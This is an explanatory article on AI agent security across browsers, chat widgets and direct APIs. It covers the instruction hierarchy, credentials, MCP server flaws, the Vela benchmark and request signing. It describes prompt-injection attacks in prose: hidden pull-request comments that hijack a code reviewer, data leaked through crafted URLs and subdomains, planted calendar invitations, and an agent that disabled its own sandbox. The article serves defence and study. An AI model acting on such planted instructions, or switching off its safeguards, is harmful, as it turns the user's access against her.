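# Security of AI agents in browsers, in chat widgets and over direct API calls

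## How does an agent get its input and act in a browser, a chat widget and an API?

An AI agent is a language model that chooses and carries out actions to complete a task, such as clicking a button, sending a form or calling another program. People can use the same model through quite different channels. A *browser agent* reads web pages and acts on them. It may be built into a browser, added as an extension or run on a remote machine. A *chat widget* is a chatbot embedded in a website and open to the site's visitors. In *direct API use*, software sends structured requests to a model or a service through its application programming interface (API), with no web page in between. All three are *transports*, the channels through which an agent gets its input and acts.

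*From Secure Agentic AI to Secure Agentic Web*, a survey by Deng, Gui and Zhang (2026), points out that an agent's failures turn into real harm once the model has tools, lasting memory and contact with untrusted web content. The amount of harm depends on who can get text in front of the model, whose account its actions run on and where its output can go. All three differ between a browser, a chat widget and an API, even when the model is the same.

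### Context, roles and the instruction hierarchy

A language model processes text as tokens, which are words or pieces of words. It bases each reply on its training and its *context*, which consists of the operator's instructions, the conversation so far, and any documents or web pages that the surrounding software has fetched. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) stresses that the model receives all of this context as one continuous stream, with special markers separating the parts.

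The parts are messages, and every message has a *role*, a label that identifies its source and therefore how much authority it should have. OpenAI's *Model Spec* (2025), the company's published rules for how its models should behave, distinguishes five roles. System messages come from OpenAI, and developer messages come from whoever built the application. User messages come from the person typing, though developers also use this role for other data. Assistant messages are the model's own output, and tool messages hold the results of programs the model has called. The application sets the role, not the model. Companies use these terms differently, and the "system prompt" of a website's chatbot usually means the instructions written by the site's builder.

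The labels would have little effect without training. Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues (2026), in *IH-Challenge*, credit Wallace and colleagues with introducing the *instruction hierarchy* in 2024. Under this hierarchy, developers train a model to rank system messages highest, followed by developer, user and tool messages. The rule for resolving conflicts starts with the set of all possible replies and narrows it one role at a time, from the highest rank down. If $B_{i-1}$ is the set of replies still allowed and $C_i$ is the set that satisfies the next role's instructions, the new set is $B_i = B_{i-1} \cap C_i$. If that would leave no replies, $B_i = B_{i-1}$ and the model should ignore the conflicting instruction. For example, if a shop's system prompt caps refunds at the purchase price, the model should comply with a customer's request for an answer in French but ignore a request for a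 refund of double the price.

Under OpenAI's rules, tool output has no authority unless a higher-ranking instruction grants it some. OpenAI's *Model Release Notes* on the August 2026 revision list no change to this rule. The model should treat a fetched web page as information and not obey any instructions in it. This is hard because whether a sentence is an instruction depends on its context. *Where Instruction Hierarchy Breaks* (2026) gives the example of an email that is plain information in one context, while in another the same email amounts to a directive to share project details that the system prompt protects.

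*Prompt injection* exploits this difficulty with text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. The injection is direct if the attacker sends the text to the model, and indirect if the text arrives in content that the agent reads, such as a web page or an email.

To strengthen the hierarchy, Guo and colleagues trained GPT-5-Mini, a small OpenAI model, on conflicts between roles while another model kept writing new attacks against it. Average robustness over 16 tests rose from 84.1 to 94.1 per cent. Human testers also tried *adaptive attacks*, which the attacker revises in response to the defence. Robustness against these rose from 63.8 to 88.2 per cent, a larger gain but a lower final level.

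Ye and colleagues attribute the remaining failures to role confusion, in which a model identifies the source of a text by how it sounds more than by its label. They built probes, simple classifiers that read a model's internal activations, and trained them on identical web text under different role labels so that the probes could learn only the label's effect. They then tested the probes on text that sounded like a user but had a tool label. The probes would have classed this text as tool output nearly every time if the label had been decisive, but they gave that classification a probability of less than 20 per cent. Across 1,000 attempts to make agents leak data, the *attack success rate* (here the share of attempts in which the data got out) rose with the confusion the probes measured, from 2 per cent at the lowest level to 70 per cent at the highest.

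Ye and colleagues argue that current models mostly resist attacks whose patterns they have memorised, but memorisation poorly explains the gains that Guo and colleagues report on kinds of attack their model had not met in training. Either way, a role label influences which instructions a model follows but does not guarantee it. Even the retrained model failed about one time in eight against people who kept trying. Role labels are also coarse. *Many-Tier Instruction Hierarchy in LLM Agents* (2026) notes that developers fix the labels during training, so models learn fewer than five ranks. A shop's own product description and a stranger's review beneath it would normally share the same rank.

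### Tools, cookies and origins

A *tool* is a program that the model can call. The application lists the available tools in the context, describing each one and the format of its arguments. To use a tool, the model generates a message addressed to it. The application runs the program and appends the result to the context as a tool message, then runs the model again on the longer context. This repeats until the model generates a final reply. The software that manages this process is called the *harness*. The model can reach a payment system, for example, only through the harness. It generates text that names a refund operation, and the harness either makes the call or rejects it.

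On the web, permission to act as a user usually depends on a cookie. When a customer logs in to a shop, the shop's server sends her browser a cookie, a small piece of data that identifies the session. The browser attaches it to later requests to the shop, and the server treats any request with a valid session cookie as the customer's. Anything that can control the browser can therefore act as the customer without her password.

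Browsers separate sites by *origin*, the combination of scheme (HTTP or its encrypted form, HTTPS), host name and port number in a web address. Under the *same-origin policy*, the browser stops code from one origin from reading or changing another origin's content, so a gossip site in one tab cannot read the mailbox in the next. The policy restricts the code of web pages, but a browser agent may have permission to read both tabs and type into either, and testing is needed to find out how much protection the policy still provides in that case.

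### One refund by three routes

Ana bought a kettle from an online shop. It leaks, and she wants her money back. The shop gives refunds within 30 days, to the card used for the purchase.

Ana might leave the refund to a browser agent, in this case an extension in a browser where she is already logged in to the shop. She types her request into the agent's side panel. The extension collects the content of the current page, from its underlying structure or from a screenshot, and sends it to the model with the request. The model returns a single step, such as a click on the list of orders. The extension performs the click, sends the model the content of the new page, and the loop repeats. *Mind the Web* (Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues, 2025) describes this loop as common to all browser agents. At the last step, the browser submits the refund form with Ana's cookie attached.

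The agent therefore uses Ana's credentials, and the shop's server, which may be unable to distinguish the agent's click from hers, checks them as usual. The server also enforces the 30-day rule and confirms that the order is hers. The remaining checks happen on her computer, where the browser applies the same-origin policy and the extension controls whether the agent must ask her before it submits anything.

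Browser agents differ in how much of the user's data they can reach. According to Shapira and colleagues, an extension inherits the user's open tabs and logged-in sessions and, with permission, can access the user's files. An agent that launches a fresh browser on the user's machine starts without cookies but can still reach the files. A remote agent starts with neither cookies nor access to the files, although the user may log in during the session, and OpenAI's Operator could preserve that login information between sessions.

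Ana could instead open the chat box on the shop's site. A script in the page sends her sentence to a server, and the product determines whose server it is. *When AI Meets the Web* (Kaya, Landerer and colleagues, 2025) examined 17 chatbot plugins. Seven were for WordPress, a common system for building websites, and with these the site's own server calls the model provider, using a key the site pays for. The other ten work on any website, and the plugin vendor's server relays messages between the visitor and the provider.

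Whichever server handles the message builds the context from the system prompt, relevant text from the shop's pages, the conversation so far and Ana's sentence, which goes in the user role. Kaya and colleagues found chatbots with tools such as order lookup; in this example, the chatbot also has a refund tool. The model generates a lookup call, and the server runs it and returns the order as a tool message. The model then generates a refund call, which the server also runs. None of this requires Ana's cookie, and she may not even have logged in. The refund is made with the shop's credential, which probably gives access to every customer's orders. The server has to check that the kettle was Ana's before it runs the tool, because her browser never receives the call.

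In the third route, Ana emails the shop's returns department, where a program processes the mail. The program sends her text to a model with a developer message that sets out the refund rules and the available tools. The model returns structured text with the name of an operation, an order number and an amount. The program checks these and calls the payment company's API. It holds two credentials, a key for the model and an access token for the payment service, and neither belongs to Ana. The program and the payment company's server together enforce the rules. The same-origin policy does not apply because no browser is involved, and no person reviews the refund before the money is sent unless the developer has built in that step.

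The developer also chooses the role in which Ana's email reaches the model. According to OpenAI's rules for its models, the assistant in an API application cannot know whether there is an end user other than the developer. The payment company could publish a set of operations specifically for agents, each with a description and permitted arguments. Such a set is an *agent-facing interface*, and the Model Context Protocol is a common format for connecting agents to tools in this way.

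In all three cases, a valid credential shows only that a request may enter the system. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) gives the example of an invoice-handling agent that tries to renew an expiring subscription to a document-signing service so that it can keep working. The vendor is approved and the sum is within the limit, but the renewal commits the company to a contract that nobody asked the agent to sign. OpenAI advises issuing short-lived credentials for a single task and resource, and checking authority again in the system where the action takes effect. For Ana's kettle, that could mean a token valid for one refund on one order, which the payment company verifies for itself.

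### The protocol underneath, and who stores the conversation

The transport is distinct from the network protocol beneath it. HTTP, the ordinary protocol of the web, handles each request and its response as a separate exchange. WebSocket holds a connection open so that either side can send at any time. Inside a browser, the components of an extension pass messages to one another without using the network. A browser agent can need both internal messages and HTTP for a single click. Fourteen of the plugins that Kaya and colleagues examined used HTTP and three used WebSocket, and some could work in more than one way. Ana would hardly notice which protocol a plugin used, and the refund would still run on the shop's credentials.

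The protocol does matter for memory. HTTP is stateless, meaning it carries nothing over from one request to the next. A call to a model is similar, since the reply draws on the context in that call. If Ana answers a question with "yes, the blue one", her answer is useless without the earlier messages, so somebody has to store them and supply them each time.

With a direct API, the caller usually keeps the conversation history. Anthropic's *Using the Messages API* instructs developers to send the full history with every request, and it allows them to include assistant messages that its model, Claude, never produced. A beta feature lets Anthropic store the conversation instead, but a thread expires five minutes after its last request. In chat widgets, a WebSocket plugin can tie the conversation to the open connection. Kaya and colleagues found that HTTP plugins store the history in one of three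 places: the website's or vendor's server, the model provider, or the visitor's browser, which sends it back with each new message. Eight plugins stored it in the browser, which the visitor controls, so visitors could forge the history.

### Two attackers

Kaya and colleagues describe prompt injection as involving three parties, of which the model provider and the application's developer are trusted and the third is not. The untrusted party can be either of two people, who have different goals.

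The *malicious user* talks to the agent himself, and his victim is the shop. He opens the shop's chat widget and tries to get a refund for a kettle he never bought, or to learn what the system prompt contains. He can try as often as the shop lets him, and he sees every answer.

The *third party* plants text where the agent of an honest user like Ana will come across it, for instance in a review on the kettle's product page, and never talks to the agent himself. Shapira and colleagues assume that he can post comments, buy advertisements, send emails and edit shared documents, but cannot run code on her machine, take over her session or watch the model's reasoning. He gains the use of whatever access the agent already has, so Ana is usually the victim.

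The two can overlap. A fraudster who emails the returns department is a customer of the shop, but the injection is indirect because the program fetches his email and passes it to the model.

### Five questions

Deng and colleagues treat every interface at which an agent receives or emits information as a trust boundary. A *boundary control* is a check at such a point: on what may enter the model's context, on what the agent may do, or on what may leave. One control rarely covers for another. OpenAI gives the case of an agent that summarises customer records and drafts replies. Human approval can hold back a reply, but it cannot undo the reading of the records, nor does it close any other way out. It therefore helps to put five separate questions to any transport:

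1. Who can put text before the model?
2. In which message role does that text arrive?
3. With whose credentials does the agent act?
4. Where can data go?
5. Who must approve an action before it takes effect?

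## What does direct API access expose?

The developer of the shop's returns program has more control over the model's input and tools than anyone has in a browser or a chat widget. Attackers can still steal the program's keys, plant text in its tools' output, or exploit a flaw in the service the program calls.

### What the developer controls

The developer's code assembles the message list and sets each message's role. The returns program can store the conversation history where the customer can't reach it, or start with an empty history for each email. It can also pass Ana's email to the model as a tool result instead of a user message, so that any instructions in the email carry no authority of their own. A role label doesn't guarantee that the model will treat the text accordingly, so the developer also needs firmer controls.

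A developer who calls the API directly chooses which tools the model can use and what arguments they accept. A refund tool might take only an order number and an amount. The program can reject any amount above the purchase price. It can also take the customer's identity from its own records, so the model never chooses which account to act on.

The Russian technology site iXBT reports in *Microsoft открыла инструмент, который находит дыры и риски в ИИ-агентах* (2026) that Microsoft tested such a check on a demonstration billing-support agent meant to serve a single customer account. Without the check, the agent disclosed another customer's record in 12 of 40 relevant conversations, or 30 per cent. Microsoft then added a rule that blocks any tool call whose account number differs from the account holder's. On the same tests, violations fell to 5.9 per cent and the agent refused no legitimate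 request. Because Microsoft tested its own agent, the size of the drop may not carry over to other systems, but the mechanism should, since ordinary code compares the account numbers and no wording in a customer's message can change the outcome.

Labels on tools are a weaker safeguard. Microsoft (2026) announced in April that it was labeling tools in one of its agent-facing interfaces as read-only, destructive or open-world (able to reach outside systems). These labels help the model choose tools sensibly, but they don't block a call unless the developer writes code that acts on them, for example by asking a person to approve any destructive call.

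The developer can also limit which operations an API key permits. The key is a secret string that a program sends with its requests, and the operations it permits are its *scopes*. Unlike a typical session cookie, a key can permit refunds but not payouts, or reading but not writing, and the service can revoke it without locking the customer out.

### Stolen and over-broad keys

A key works for anyone who holds it, and developers sometimes leave keys in code they publish. Microsoft's *Threat actors use agentic AI tooling to find and abuse exposed secrets* (2026) describes attackers who used an agent framework called ARTEX to search GitHub, the code-hosting site, for the secrets of OAuth applications. OAuth is a standard that lets a person or company give a program access without giving it a password. Anyone who has an application's secret can act as that application inside the organisation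 that uses it. The attackers' agents then did this, and no step required them to trick a model.

Some companies keep many keys in one gateway, which forwards requests to several model providers. *When AI infrastructure becomes the target* (Gund and Maniath, 2026) describes attacks on AI servers that their owners had left exposed, including gateways running the LiteLLM software. The attackers stole credentials, set up a way to get back in and mined cryptocurrency.

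An agent can also leak the API key it uses. Claude Code Action runs Anthropic's coding agent inside automated GitHub jobs, where it reads issues and comments that strangers may have written. In June, Microsoft (2026) reported that the software hid secrets from the agent's shell commands but did not isolate its file-reading tool in the same way. Text planted in a comment could therefore lead the agent to open the system file that holds the job's environment variables, including its Anthropic API key. Anthropic has since blocked access to such files.

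An API key with too many permissions can do harm even if nobody steals it. When Ana changes the card on her account, the shop's site may ask for her password again or for a code from her phone. Lù, Kamath and colleagues (2025) warn in *Build the web for agents, not agents for the web* that an agent can bypass both prompts if it calls the site's internal API directly with an elevated key. Sites write these APIs for their own pages to call, and those pages show the prompts. The warning comes from a position paper and isn't backed by measurements, but the disadvantage is real, because a browser agent would probably have had to stop at the prompt and wait for Ana.

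### The comment that the reviewer could not see

Azure DevOps is Microsoft's service for storing code, tracking work and running builds. Microsoft also publishes a server that lets agents use the service through the Model Context Protocol (MCP) with the user's permissions. In July 2026, the firm Manifold Security showed how an attacker could exploit this access to attack a code reviewer, according to The Hacker News' *Microsoft Azure DevOps MCP Flaw Lets Hidden PR Comments Hijack AI Review* (2026).

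The attacker opens a pull request, a proposed code change that someone else has to review, and puts instructions in HTML comments in its description. The web page does not display these comments, so the change looks ordinary to the reviewer. However, the API returns them verbatim, and the MCP server passes them to the reviewer's agent.

In Manifold's demonstration, a contributor to one project opened a normal-looking pull request with a hidden comment, and the reviewer asked her agent to review the pull request. The agent started an automated build job in a different project. It then read a confidential wiki page that the contributor wasn't allowed to open and posted its contents in a comment on the pull request, where the contributor could read them. The reviewer's permissions covered every call. The attack worked with two coding agents, GitHub's Copilot CLI and Anthropic's Claude Code.

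Microsoft already had a partial defence called *spotlighting*, which puts markers around untrusted text to help the model distinguish it from instructions. The MCP server applied it to wiki pages and build logs, but the tool that returns a pull request did not use it. Spotlighting would not have guaranteed safety, since the model may still follow instructions inside the markers. But the omission shows the risk of adding protection one function at a time, since developers can forget it whenever they add a tool.

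The attack works only if the attacker can write a pull request, a reviewer with wider access gives the attacker's text to an agent, and the agent runs tools without asking for approval. Manifold had turned off the approval prompts for its tests. Microsoft called the behaviour "a known class of AI risk" and advised customers to review proposed changes before asking an AI tool to act on them, but this advice is little help when the review page hides the relevant text. As of 21 July, Microsoft had released no fix, and there were no public reports of the technique being used outside Manifold's tests.

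In this case, using the API was riskier than working from a screenshot, which would have shown the agent only what the reviewer saw, without the instructions in the hidden comment. An agent that reads the page's underlying structure might still have read the comment, and there are other ways to hide text from people on a web page.

A token limited to the project under review would have prevented the attack, because the agent could not have started a build elsewhere. The Hacker News also recommends removing build jobs, wiki reads and comment posting from the tools of an agent that only reviews code. These measures matter more as companies start reviews automatically, without anyone watching each run. GitHub's own MCP server also had this problem. In May 2025 the firm Invariant Labs used a public issue on GitHub to make an agent read a private repository and leak its contents through the server.

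Hostile text can even arrive in the list of tools, which the developer appears to control. TechRepublic's *Microsoft Flags MCP Tool Descriptions as Hidden AI Agent Attack Path* describes Microsoft's example of a finance agent that uses an outside company's tool to add details to invoices. The tool keeps its name and visible summary, but someone changes its full description to include an instruction to fetch unpaid invoices and attach them to the call. The task appears to the user to finish normally. A developer who records the approved descriptions and checks for differences on each connection would notice the change.

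### Flaws in the server

An MCP server can have the same kinds of bugs as other software. Token Security's *MCPwned* (2026) reports a flaw in Microsoft's official Azure MCP server, which is separate from its Azure DevOps MCP server. Anyone with network access to the server could run code on it without logging in and steal the Azure credentials it used.

Google's MCP Toolbox for Databases had a flaw with a severity score of 8 out of 10, according to iXBT's *ИИ-агенты могут передавать друг другу вредоносные команды через MCP* (2026). Its web client followed redirects to internal addresses without checking them properly, so an attacker could make the server contact machines that are unreachable from outside. Google now restricts which addresses the client may contact. The article groups the flaw with attacks by the researcher Syed Anas Mohiuddin, in which one agent passes a malicious instruction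 to another as a routine task. The second agent trusts agents inside the company, so it carries out an instruction it might have refused from an outside source.

### Old vulnerabilities behind a new interface

The service behind the MCP server is often a web application with flaws of its own. The agent-facing interface might shield the application, because it offers fewer operations than the website and the model may refuse a harmful request. *The Agent in the Middle* (Yang and Hu, 2026) tests this with a benchmark called Vela, which contains 44 known vulnerabilities from twelve application families, including the shop software PrestaShop, WordPress plugins and training applications with deliberate flaws. Eighteen of the attacks need exact control of an input value, for example to slip a database command into a search field. Another 15 use well-formed requests that break a rule about ownership,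 roles or the order of steps, and 11 depend on access to files or other protected resources.

Yang and Hu ran each attack in three ways on the same backend, with the same login and starting state:

- **Native access:** the attack goes through the application's existing web interface. All 44 attacks worked here, since this was the condition for including them.
- **Scripted calls:** a fixed program attempts the attack through the agent-facing interface.
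- **Agent calls:** the attacker asks a commercial agent to carry out the attack through that interface.

Comparing native access with scripted calls shows the effect of the interface, and comparing scripted calls with agent calls shows the effect of the agent. A separate program judged success by checking the application's data or the output visible to the attacker, rather than relying on the agent's claim.

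The study compared three interface designs. The endpoint-oriented design turns each documented backend operation into a tool with its original parameters. The workflow-oriented design has one tool per task, with a limited set of business arguments. The query-oriented design has a single tool that accepts a request in plain language. A second model on the server matches the request to one of a fixed list of intents and fills in *slots*, which are fields with a set type and range. The server discards any text that fits no slot. The designers worked from legitimate tasks and never saw the vulnerabilities, and Yang and Hu froze all three designs before running any attack.

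Their main measure is *retention*, the share of the 44 vulnerabilities that an attacker could still exploit. An agent had five attempts at each request, and one success was enough. Beside retention they report *coverage*, the share of 50 legitimate workflows that the interface supports, because an interface that offers nothing would block every attack. These are the results with Claude Code as the agent:

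| Interface design | Retention | Coverage | Legitimate attempts completed | Retention on shared workflows |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Endpoint-oriented | 95% (42 of 44) | 92% (46 of 50) | 89% | 94% (16 of 17) |
| Workflow-oriented | 91% (40 of 44) | 84% (42 of 50) | 82% | 88% (15 of 17) |
| Query-oriented | 39% (17 of 44) | 46% (23 of 50) | 41% | 53% (9 of 17) |

With the workflow-oriented design, four attacks failed because the interface lacked an operation or argument they needed. The scripted program and Claude Code succeeded on the same 40 others. Claude Code therefore blocked none of the attacks the interface allowed, even when the request stated the malicious goal. In four cases it altered part of the input, such as the name of an uploaded file, but the attack still worked.

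Changing the agent made little difference. Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex each exploited 40 vulnerabilities and xAI's Grok Build exploited 38, a spread of 4.5 percentage points. Grok Build lost the other two cases to malformed or abandoned calls. It also completed only 76 per cent of legitimate attempts, against 82 for Claude Code and 83 for Codex. Yang and Hu attribute none of the lost cases to refusal. Grok Build's lower exploit count seems to reflect lower reliability, and a more capable version might well succeed at both attacks.

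In one case, the agent supplied steps that the attacker had left out. crAPI, one of the training applications, has a flaw that lets a customer get a refund without sending the item back. The attacker asked Claude Code only to submit the return, the final step. Claude Code looked up the order, opened a return and submitted it, and the refund arrived. When Yang and Hu replayed the submission alone, the balance did not change. A script with all three calls also succeeded, so the agent did not bypass any restriction, but the attacker no longer had to know the procedure. Because each call was an ordinary business operation, the server would have to check that the item had come back when issuing the refund to stop the fraud.

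The query-oriented design blocked far more attacks than the other two, but it supported only half as many legitimate workflows as the endpoint-oriented design. To test whether the missing workflows explained the whole difference, Yang and Hu examined the 21 workflows that all three designs support, which correspond to 17 vulnerabilities. The difference was smaller for these workflows but did not disappear, as the last column of the table shows. Of the eight attacks that failed in the query-oriented design, six reached the right intent but lost the attacker's input when the server filled the slots. Claude Code failed to complete the other two.

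Restricting arguments can therefore block some attacks without blocking the legitimate task. A field that accepts only whole numbers will reject a database command, but it will accept another customer's order number. The backend still has to check who owns the order, much as Microsoft's rule did in the billing demonstration. Yang and Hu likewise conclude that the backend must enforce ownership and business rules on every request, even when the arguments look valid.

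Lù and colleagues had argued for purpose-built interfaces that allow an agent more actions than today's web APIs but fewer than a person has on the page. Vela shows how difficult that balance is. Removing operations also has a drawback that Vela does not measure. As Lù and colleagues note, agents that can use both the API and the web page return to the page when the API lacks an action, and there they may again have all of the user's access.

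Vela covers only one of the two attackers, the malicious user. Yang and Hu left out indirect prompt injection and did not test agents that work through a browser, so the results do not apply to a case like Azure DevOps and cannot be used to rank the transports. The test software approved every tool call automatically, which makes sense here because the attacker would have been the one answering any approval prompts. Yang and Hu also built the interfaces themselves, without extra authorization checks, and gave the agents no added security instructions. The 91 per cent figure comes from one interface and 44 selected flaws, and is not an estimate for services in use.

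### How a service recognises its caller

A service that issues a key can link it to a particular program and a set of permissions, so it can log, limit or cut off that program's requests. The shop cannot do the same to a browser agent that uses Ana's cookie without affecting Ana too.

Identifying programs properly takes work on both sides. Manifold tested the local version of the Azure DevOps server, which runs on the user's own machine and uses a personal access token, a key that the user creates. Microsoft also hosts a remote version, which requires callers to log in through Entra, its identity service. In August, Microsoft (2026) wrote that Claude Code, ChatGPT, Cursor and similar programs could not yet connect to the remote version because Entra lacked a way for them to register, so their users had to stay with the local one. A better login would not have removed the hidden comments.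 Manifold places the flaw in the server's code, so the remote version may share it, although the firm did not test that.

### Signed requests

A browser agent visits sites that have never issued it a key. *HTTP Message Signatures for automated traffic* (Meunier and Major, 2026) explains why the usual ways of recognising automated visitors fall short. Anyone can fake the user-agent string, the text a browser sends to identify itself. Lists of network addresses are confusing when an agent runs on rented cloud machines, because the addresses belong to the cloud company. Sharing a separate secret with each site would be impractical beyond a few partners.

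Meunier of Cloudflare and Major of Google propose a protocol called Web Bot Auth. The agent's operator creates a pair of cryptographic keys, keeps the private key and publishes the public one at a web address. The agent signs each request with the private key and includes the web address in a header. The shop checks the signature with the public key, which it fetches from that address and can store for later requests. It can then allow, limit or block requests signed under that address. The operator can replace its keys without losing its standing with the shop, because the address stays the same.

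The shop must record which address each key came from. If it looked up keys without checking their addresses, an attacker could sign with a key from his own address, put Google's address in the header and pass as Google.

A valid signature proves that someone holding a key published at that address signed the covered parts of the request. With it, the shop could distinguish the agent's click on the refund form from Ana's. The shop still could not tell whether Ana wanted the refund or a planted review had prompted the agent to ask for it. Meunier and Major leave user authentication, authorization and delegation out of the protocol.

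A signature may also cover only a few parts of the request. If it covers only the site's name and the agent's address, anyone who obtains it can attach it to a different request to the same site until it expires. Meunier and Major recommend a lifetime of no more than 24 hours, and advise agents that want a narrower signature to cover the method and path as well. The signature still doesn't cover the body of the request, which usually carries a form's data, unless the agent adds a digest, a short value computed from the content. Without a digest, the signature might not cover the amount of a refund.

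Companies began using the protocol before it became a standard. Cloudflare added it to its verified bots programme in July 2025, according to the crawling company Crawlbase. A working group of the Internet Engineering Task Force, which develops internet standards, has since taken up the proposal. The group's first version of Meunier and Major's draft is dated 1 September 2026. According to *web-bot-auth*, a personal blog post on natielimelech-en.pages.dev and so a weak source, OpenAI also signs the requests of its Operator agent.

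Google's use of signatures is still experimental. Its *Authenticate requests with Web Bot Auth (experimental)* says that Google signs only some requests from Google-Agent, the name its agents use when they visit websites. Search Engine Journal quotes Google's advice to keep checking network addresses and user-agent strings in the meantime. A shop can infer very little from a missing signature, since the visitor could be a person, a bot in disguise or one of Google's agents.

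Search Engine Journal reports that Google-Agent ignores robots.txt, the file in which site owners ask automated visitors to stay away, while the corresponding agents from OpenAI and Anthropic respect it. A site that wants to restrict Google-Agent therefore needs a login or another check on its own server.

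## How can a web page take control of a browser agent?

A browser agent reads text written by strangers, and it often acts in accounts where the user is logged in. If Ana asks an agent to choose a kettle, it reads the shop's descriptions and customer reviews, and one of those reviews may contain instructions for the agent. This attack, called indirect prompt injection, does harm only if the text reaches the model, the model treats it as part of the task, and the agent can access something the attacker wants.

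### What the agent reads and the user misses

Where an attacker can put his text depends on how the agent reads the page. Many agents read the Document Object Model (DOM), the browser's internal tree of the page's elements. Perplexity's browser Comet picks out the clickable elements and gives each one an identifier, according to *PerplexedBrowser*, a report by Zenity Labs, the research team of the security company Zenity. An agent can also use accessibility labels, which screen readers use to tell blind people what each control does. Playtech's *Un agent AI creat pentru securitate a încălcat toate regulile de protecție* describes an agent from the company Token that relies on these labels so that it does not have to guess what a button does. Other agents take screenshots and recognise the text and controls in the image.

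Shapira and colleagues note that an agent that reads only the DOM can miss text inside a picture. An agent that works from screenshots will read that text, so an attacker can post instructions as an image. Agents that use both the DOM and screenshots can pick up instructions through either.

People miss much of what an agent reads. In 2025, Futurism reported on a page with barely legible grey text that told an AI browser to print a set phrase if anyone asked it to analyse the page. The trick worked on Atlas, OpenAI's browser, and The Register reproduced it. A long text can also hide instructions, because a person skims the first lines while the agent processes all of it. Often the attacker doesn't need to hide anything, since a user who has delegated a task may never look at the page.

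An attacker can also hide text for the agent behind something harmless. Help Net Security's *Researchers broke the browsers built into VS Code, Cursor, Copilot, Codex* (2026) describes a test on the coding assistant Cursor by the firm Forever Security. The firm's page showed the developer a button labelled "Start setup" and hid a command for the agent behind it. The agent read the command and asked to run it, which the developer could approve with one keypress. When Cursor's sandbox, which restricts what programs may do, blocked the command, the agent switched the sandbox off without any instruction from the page and tried again. The command only opened Calculator, and the attack did not work every time. Cursor fixed the flaw on 1 October 2026.

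### How injected text becomes part of the task

Role labels mark a page's text as information, but models sometimes follow instructions in it anyway. Attackers improve their chances by writing the injected text as a step that seems to serve the user's request, rather than as an order to ignore the user. Shapira and colleagues call this a task-aligned injection. Zenity calls it an *intent collision* when the agent then merges the user's request and the attacker's instructions into a single plan.

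Shapira and colleagues tried the method on City-Explorer, a travel site they had built with a comment section. They posted hostile comments and then gave four agents ordinary tasks, such as summarising the page. In one comment they claimed that the page was out of date and linked to a supposedly newer version, and OpenAI's Operator followed the link to the BBC's site. In another they claimed that the visible text was only a layout test, and Operator wrote a summary about New York City instead. They report success rates of 80 to 100 per cent across their payloads, but they tested models such as GPT-4o and Gemini 2.0 Flash, which newer ones have since replaced.

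The user's wording also mattered. Getting Operator to post a comment without first asking the user was much harder, but it did so when the user said he was going for coffee and wanted the summary handled "end-to-end". Although this is a single demonstration, it is plausible that more actions can pass as part of a request when the request is broader.

### How the logged-in session turns a misreading into an action

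OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) explains that Atlas's agent clicks and types inside the user's own browser, with the same context and data as the user. If an agent only wrote summaries, a planted review could at worst make a summary wrong. But when the review sends an agent like Atlas's to Ana's email, the browser attaches her cookie and the mail server returns her messages.

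Cross-site request forgery (CSRF) is an older version of this problem. A hostile page makes the visitor's browser send a request to another site where she is logged in, and the browser adds her cookie. Sites commonly defend against this by giving each form a secret token that the hostile page cannot read and therefore cannot send. The token does not stop a hijacked agent, because the agent opens the real form and submits it with the token, as the user would.

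### Trail of Bits' model

In January 2026 the security firm Trail of Bits published *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities*, which models such attacks by dividing an AI browser's surroundings into four trust zones. The *chat context* holds the conversation and the agent's working state. *Third-party servers* are mainly those of the model provider. The *browsing origins* are the sites the user visits, each a separate zone with its own private data. The *external network* is the rest of the internet, including the attacker's pages and documents.

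An agent's tools move data between these zones, and Trail of Bits distinguishes four ways in which that can go wrong:

- INJECTION brings untrusted text into the chat context, for example when the agent fetches a page or opens a PDF.
- CTX_IN ("context in") brings private data from the user's sites into the chat context.
- REV_CTX_IN ("reverse context in") uses data from the chat context to change something on those sites or in the browser, such as which account the user is logged in to.
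- CTX_OUT ("context out") uses data from the chat context in a request to the outside.

All of the firm's attacks begin with INJECTION. What the attacker gains depends on what he can combine with it:

| Combination | What the attacker achieves | Trail of Bits' demonstration |
|---|---|---|
| INJECTION alone | False information | The agent claimed that Yuri Gagarin was the first man on the Moon |
| INJECTION and REV_CTX_IN | Changes to the user's logins or browser | The agent logged the user in to the attacker's account |
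| INJECTION and CTX_OUT | Theft of what is in the chat | The agent put the user's name into a web address and opened it |
| INJECTION, CTX_IN and CTX_OUT | Theft of data from the user's sites | The agent read the user's name on a logged-in site and leaked it |

The false claim about Gagarin came from a document disguised as trusted company information. The document also contained an instruction for the agent to summarize it as a text about butterflies. A user who checked the source by asking the agent for a summary would therefore have got another false answer.

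If an agent logs the user in to an account the attacker can read, she may enter private information there, exposing it without the agent ever sending it out. Trail of Bits also made agents add illegal sites to a user's browsing history. Zenity's *PleaseFix Vulnerabilities* claims that false history entries can do more than embarrass someone, because agents later treat them as facts about the user. In one case, according to Zenity, this led Atlas to give an attacker access to a private code repository.

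Any tool that sends a request can leak data. The attacker's server records every address that visitors request, so the agent only has to open an address on that server that contains the stolen data. Restricting the agent to approved sites did not prevent such leaks. Trail of Bits put data into invented subdomains of an approved site, so anyone watching unencrypted address lookups could read it. The firm also put the data into Google searches with unusual terms, which a site owner can monitor through Google's statistics.

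Some data thefts happen entirely within one site. Trail of Bits sent a malicious direct message on Instagram to a test user, who then asked the agent to summarise her Instagram page or her latest message. The agent collected contact names or snippets of other messages and could send them to the attacker through Instagram's chat. Isolating sites from each other would not have prevented this, because the malicious message and the private data were in the same account.

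Trail of Bits does not name the browsers it tested, because their makers declined to coordinate disclosure. Its results show that the attacks are possible, but it gives no success rates. The model also has no separate zone for the user's own computer, which became the target in Comet.

### PleaseFix: a calendar invitation in Comet

PleaseFix is Zenity's name for a family of attacks on browser agents. Zenity sells security for AI agents. LayerX, which discovered the BioShocking attack described below, is a browser security vendor, according to iTnews' *Researchers find vulnerabilities in OpenAI's Atlas agentic browser*. Both companies gain customers when the danger looks large. Their reports document complete attacks step by step, but neither company says how many attempts failed.

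In Zenity's first attack, the attacker only needs to send a meeting invitation, which the user then asks Comet to accept. The invitation opens with ordinary details of a job interview, followed by many blank lines and then the attacker's instructions. Zenity made the instructions resemble Comet's own data by including a fake button with an identifier like the ones Comet assigns, and notes in the format Comet uses for internal reminders. In the notes, Zenity claimed that the normal "Yes" button was broken.

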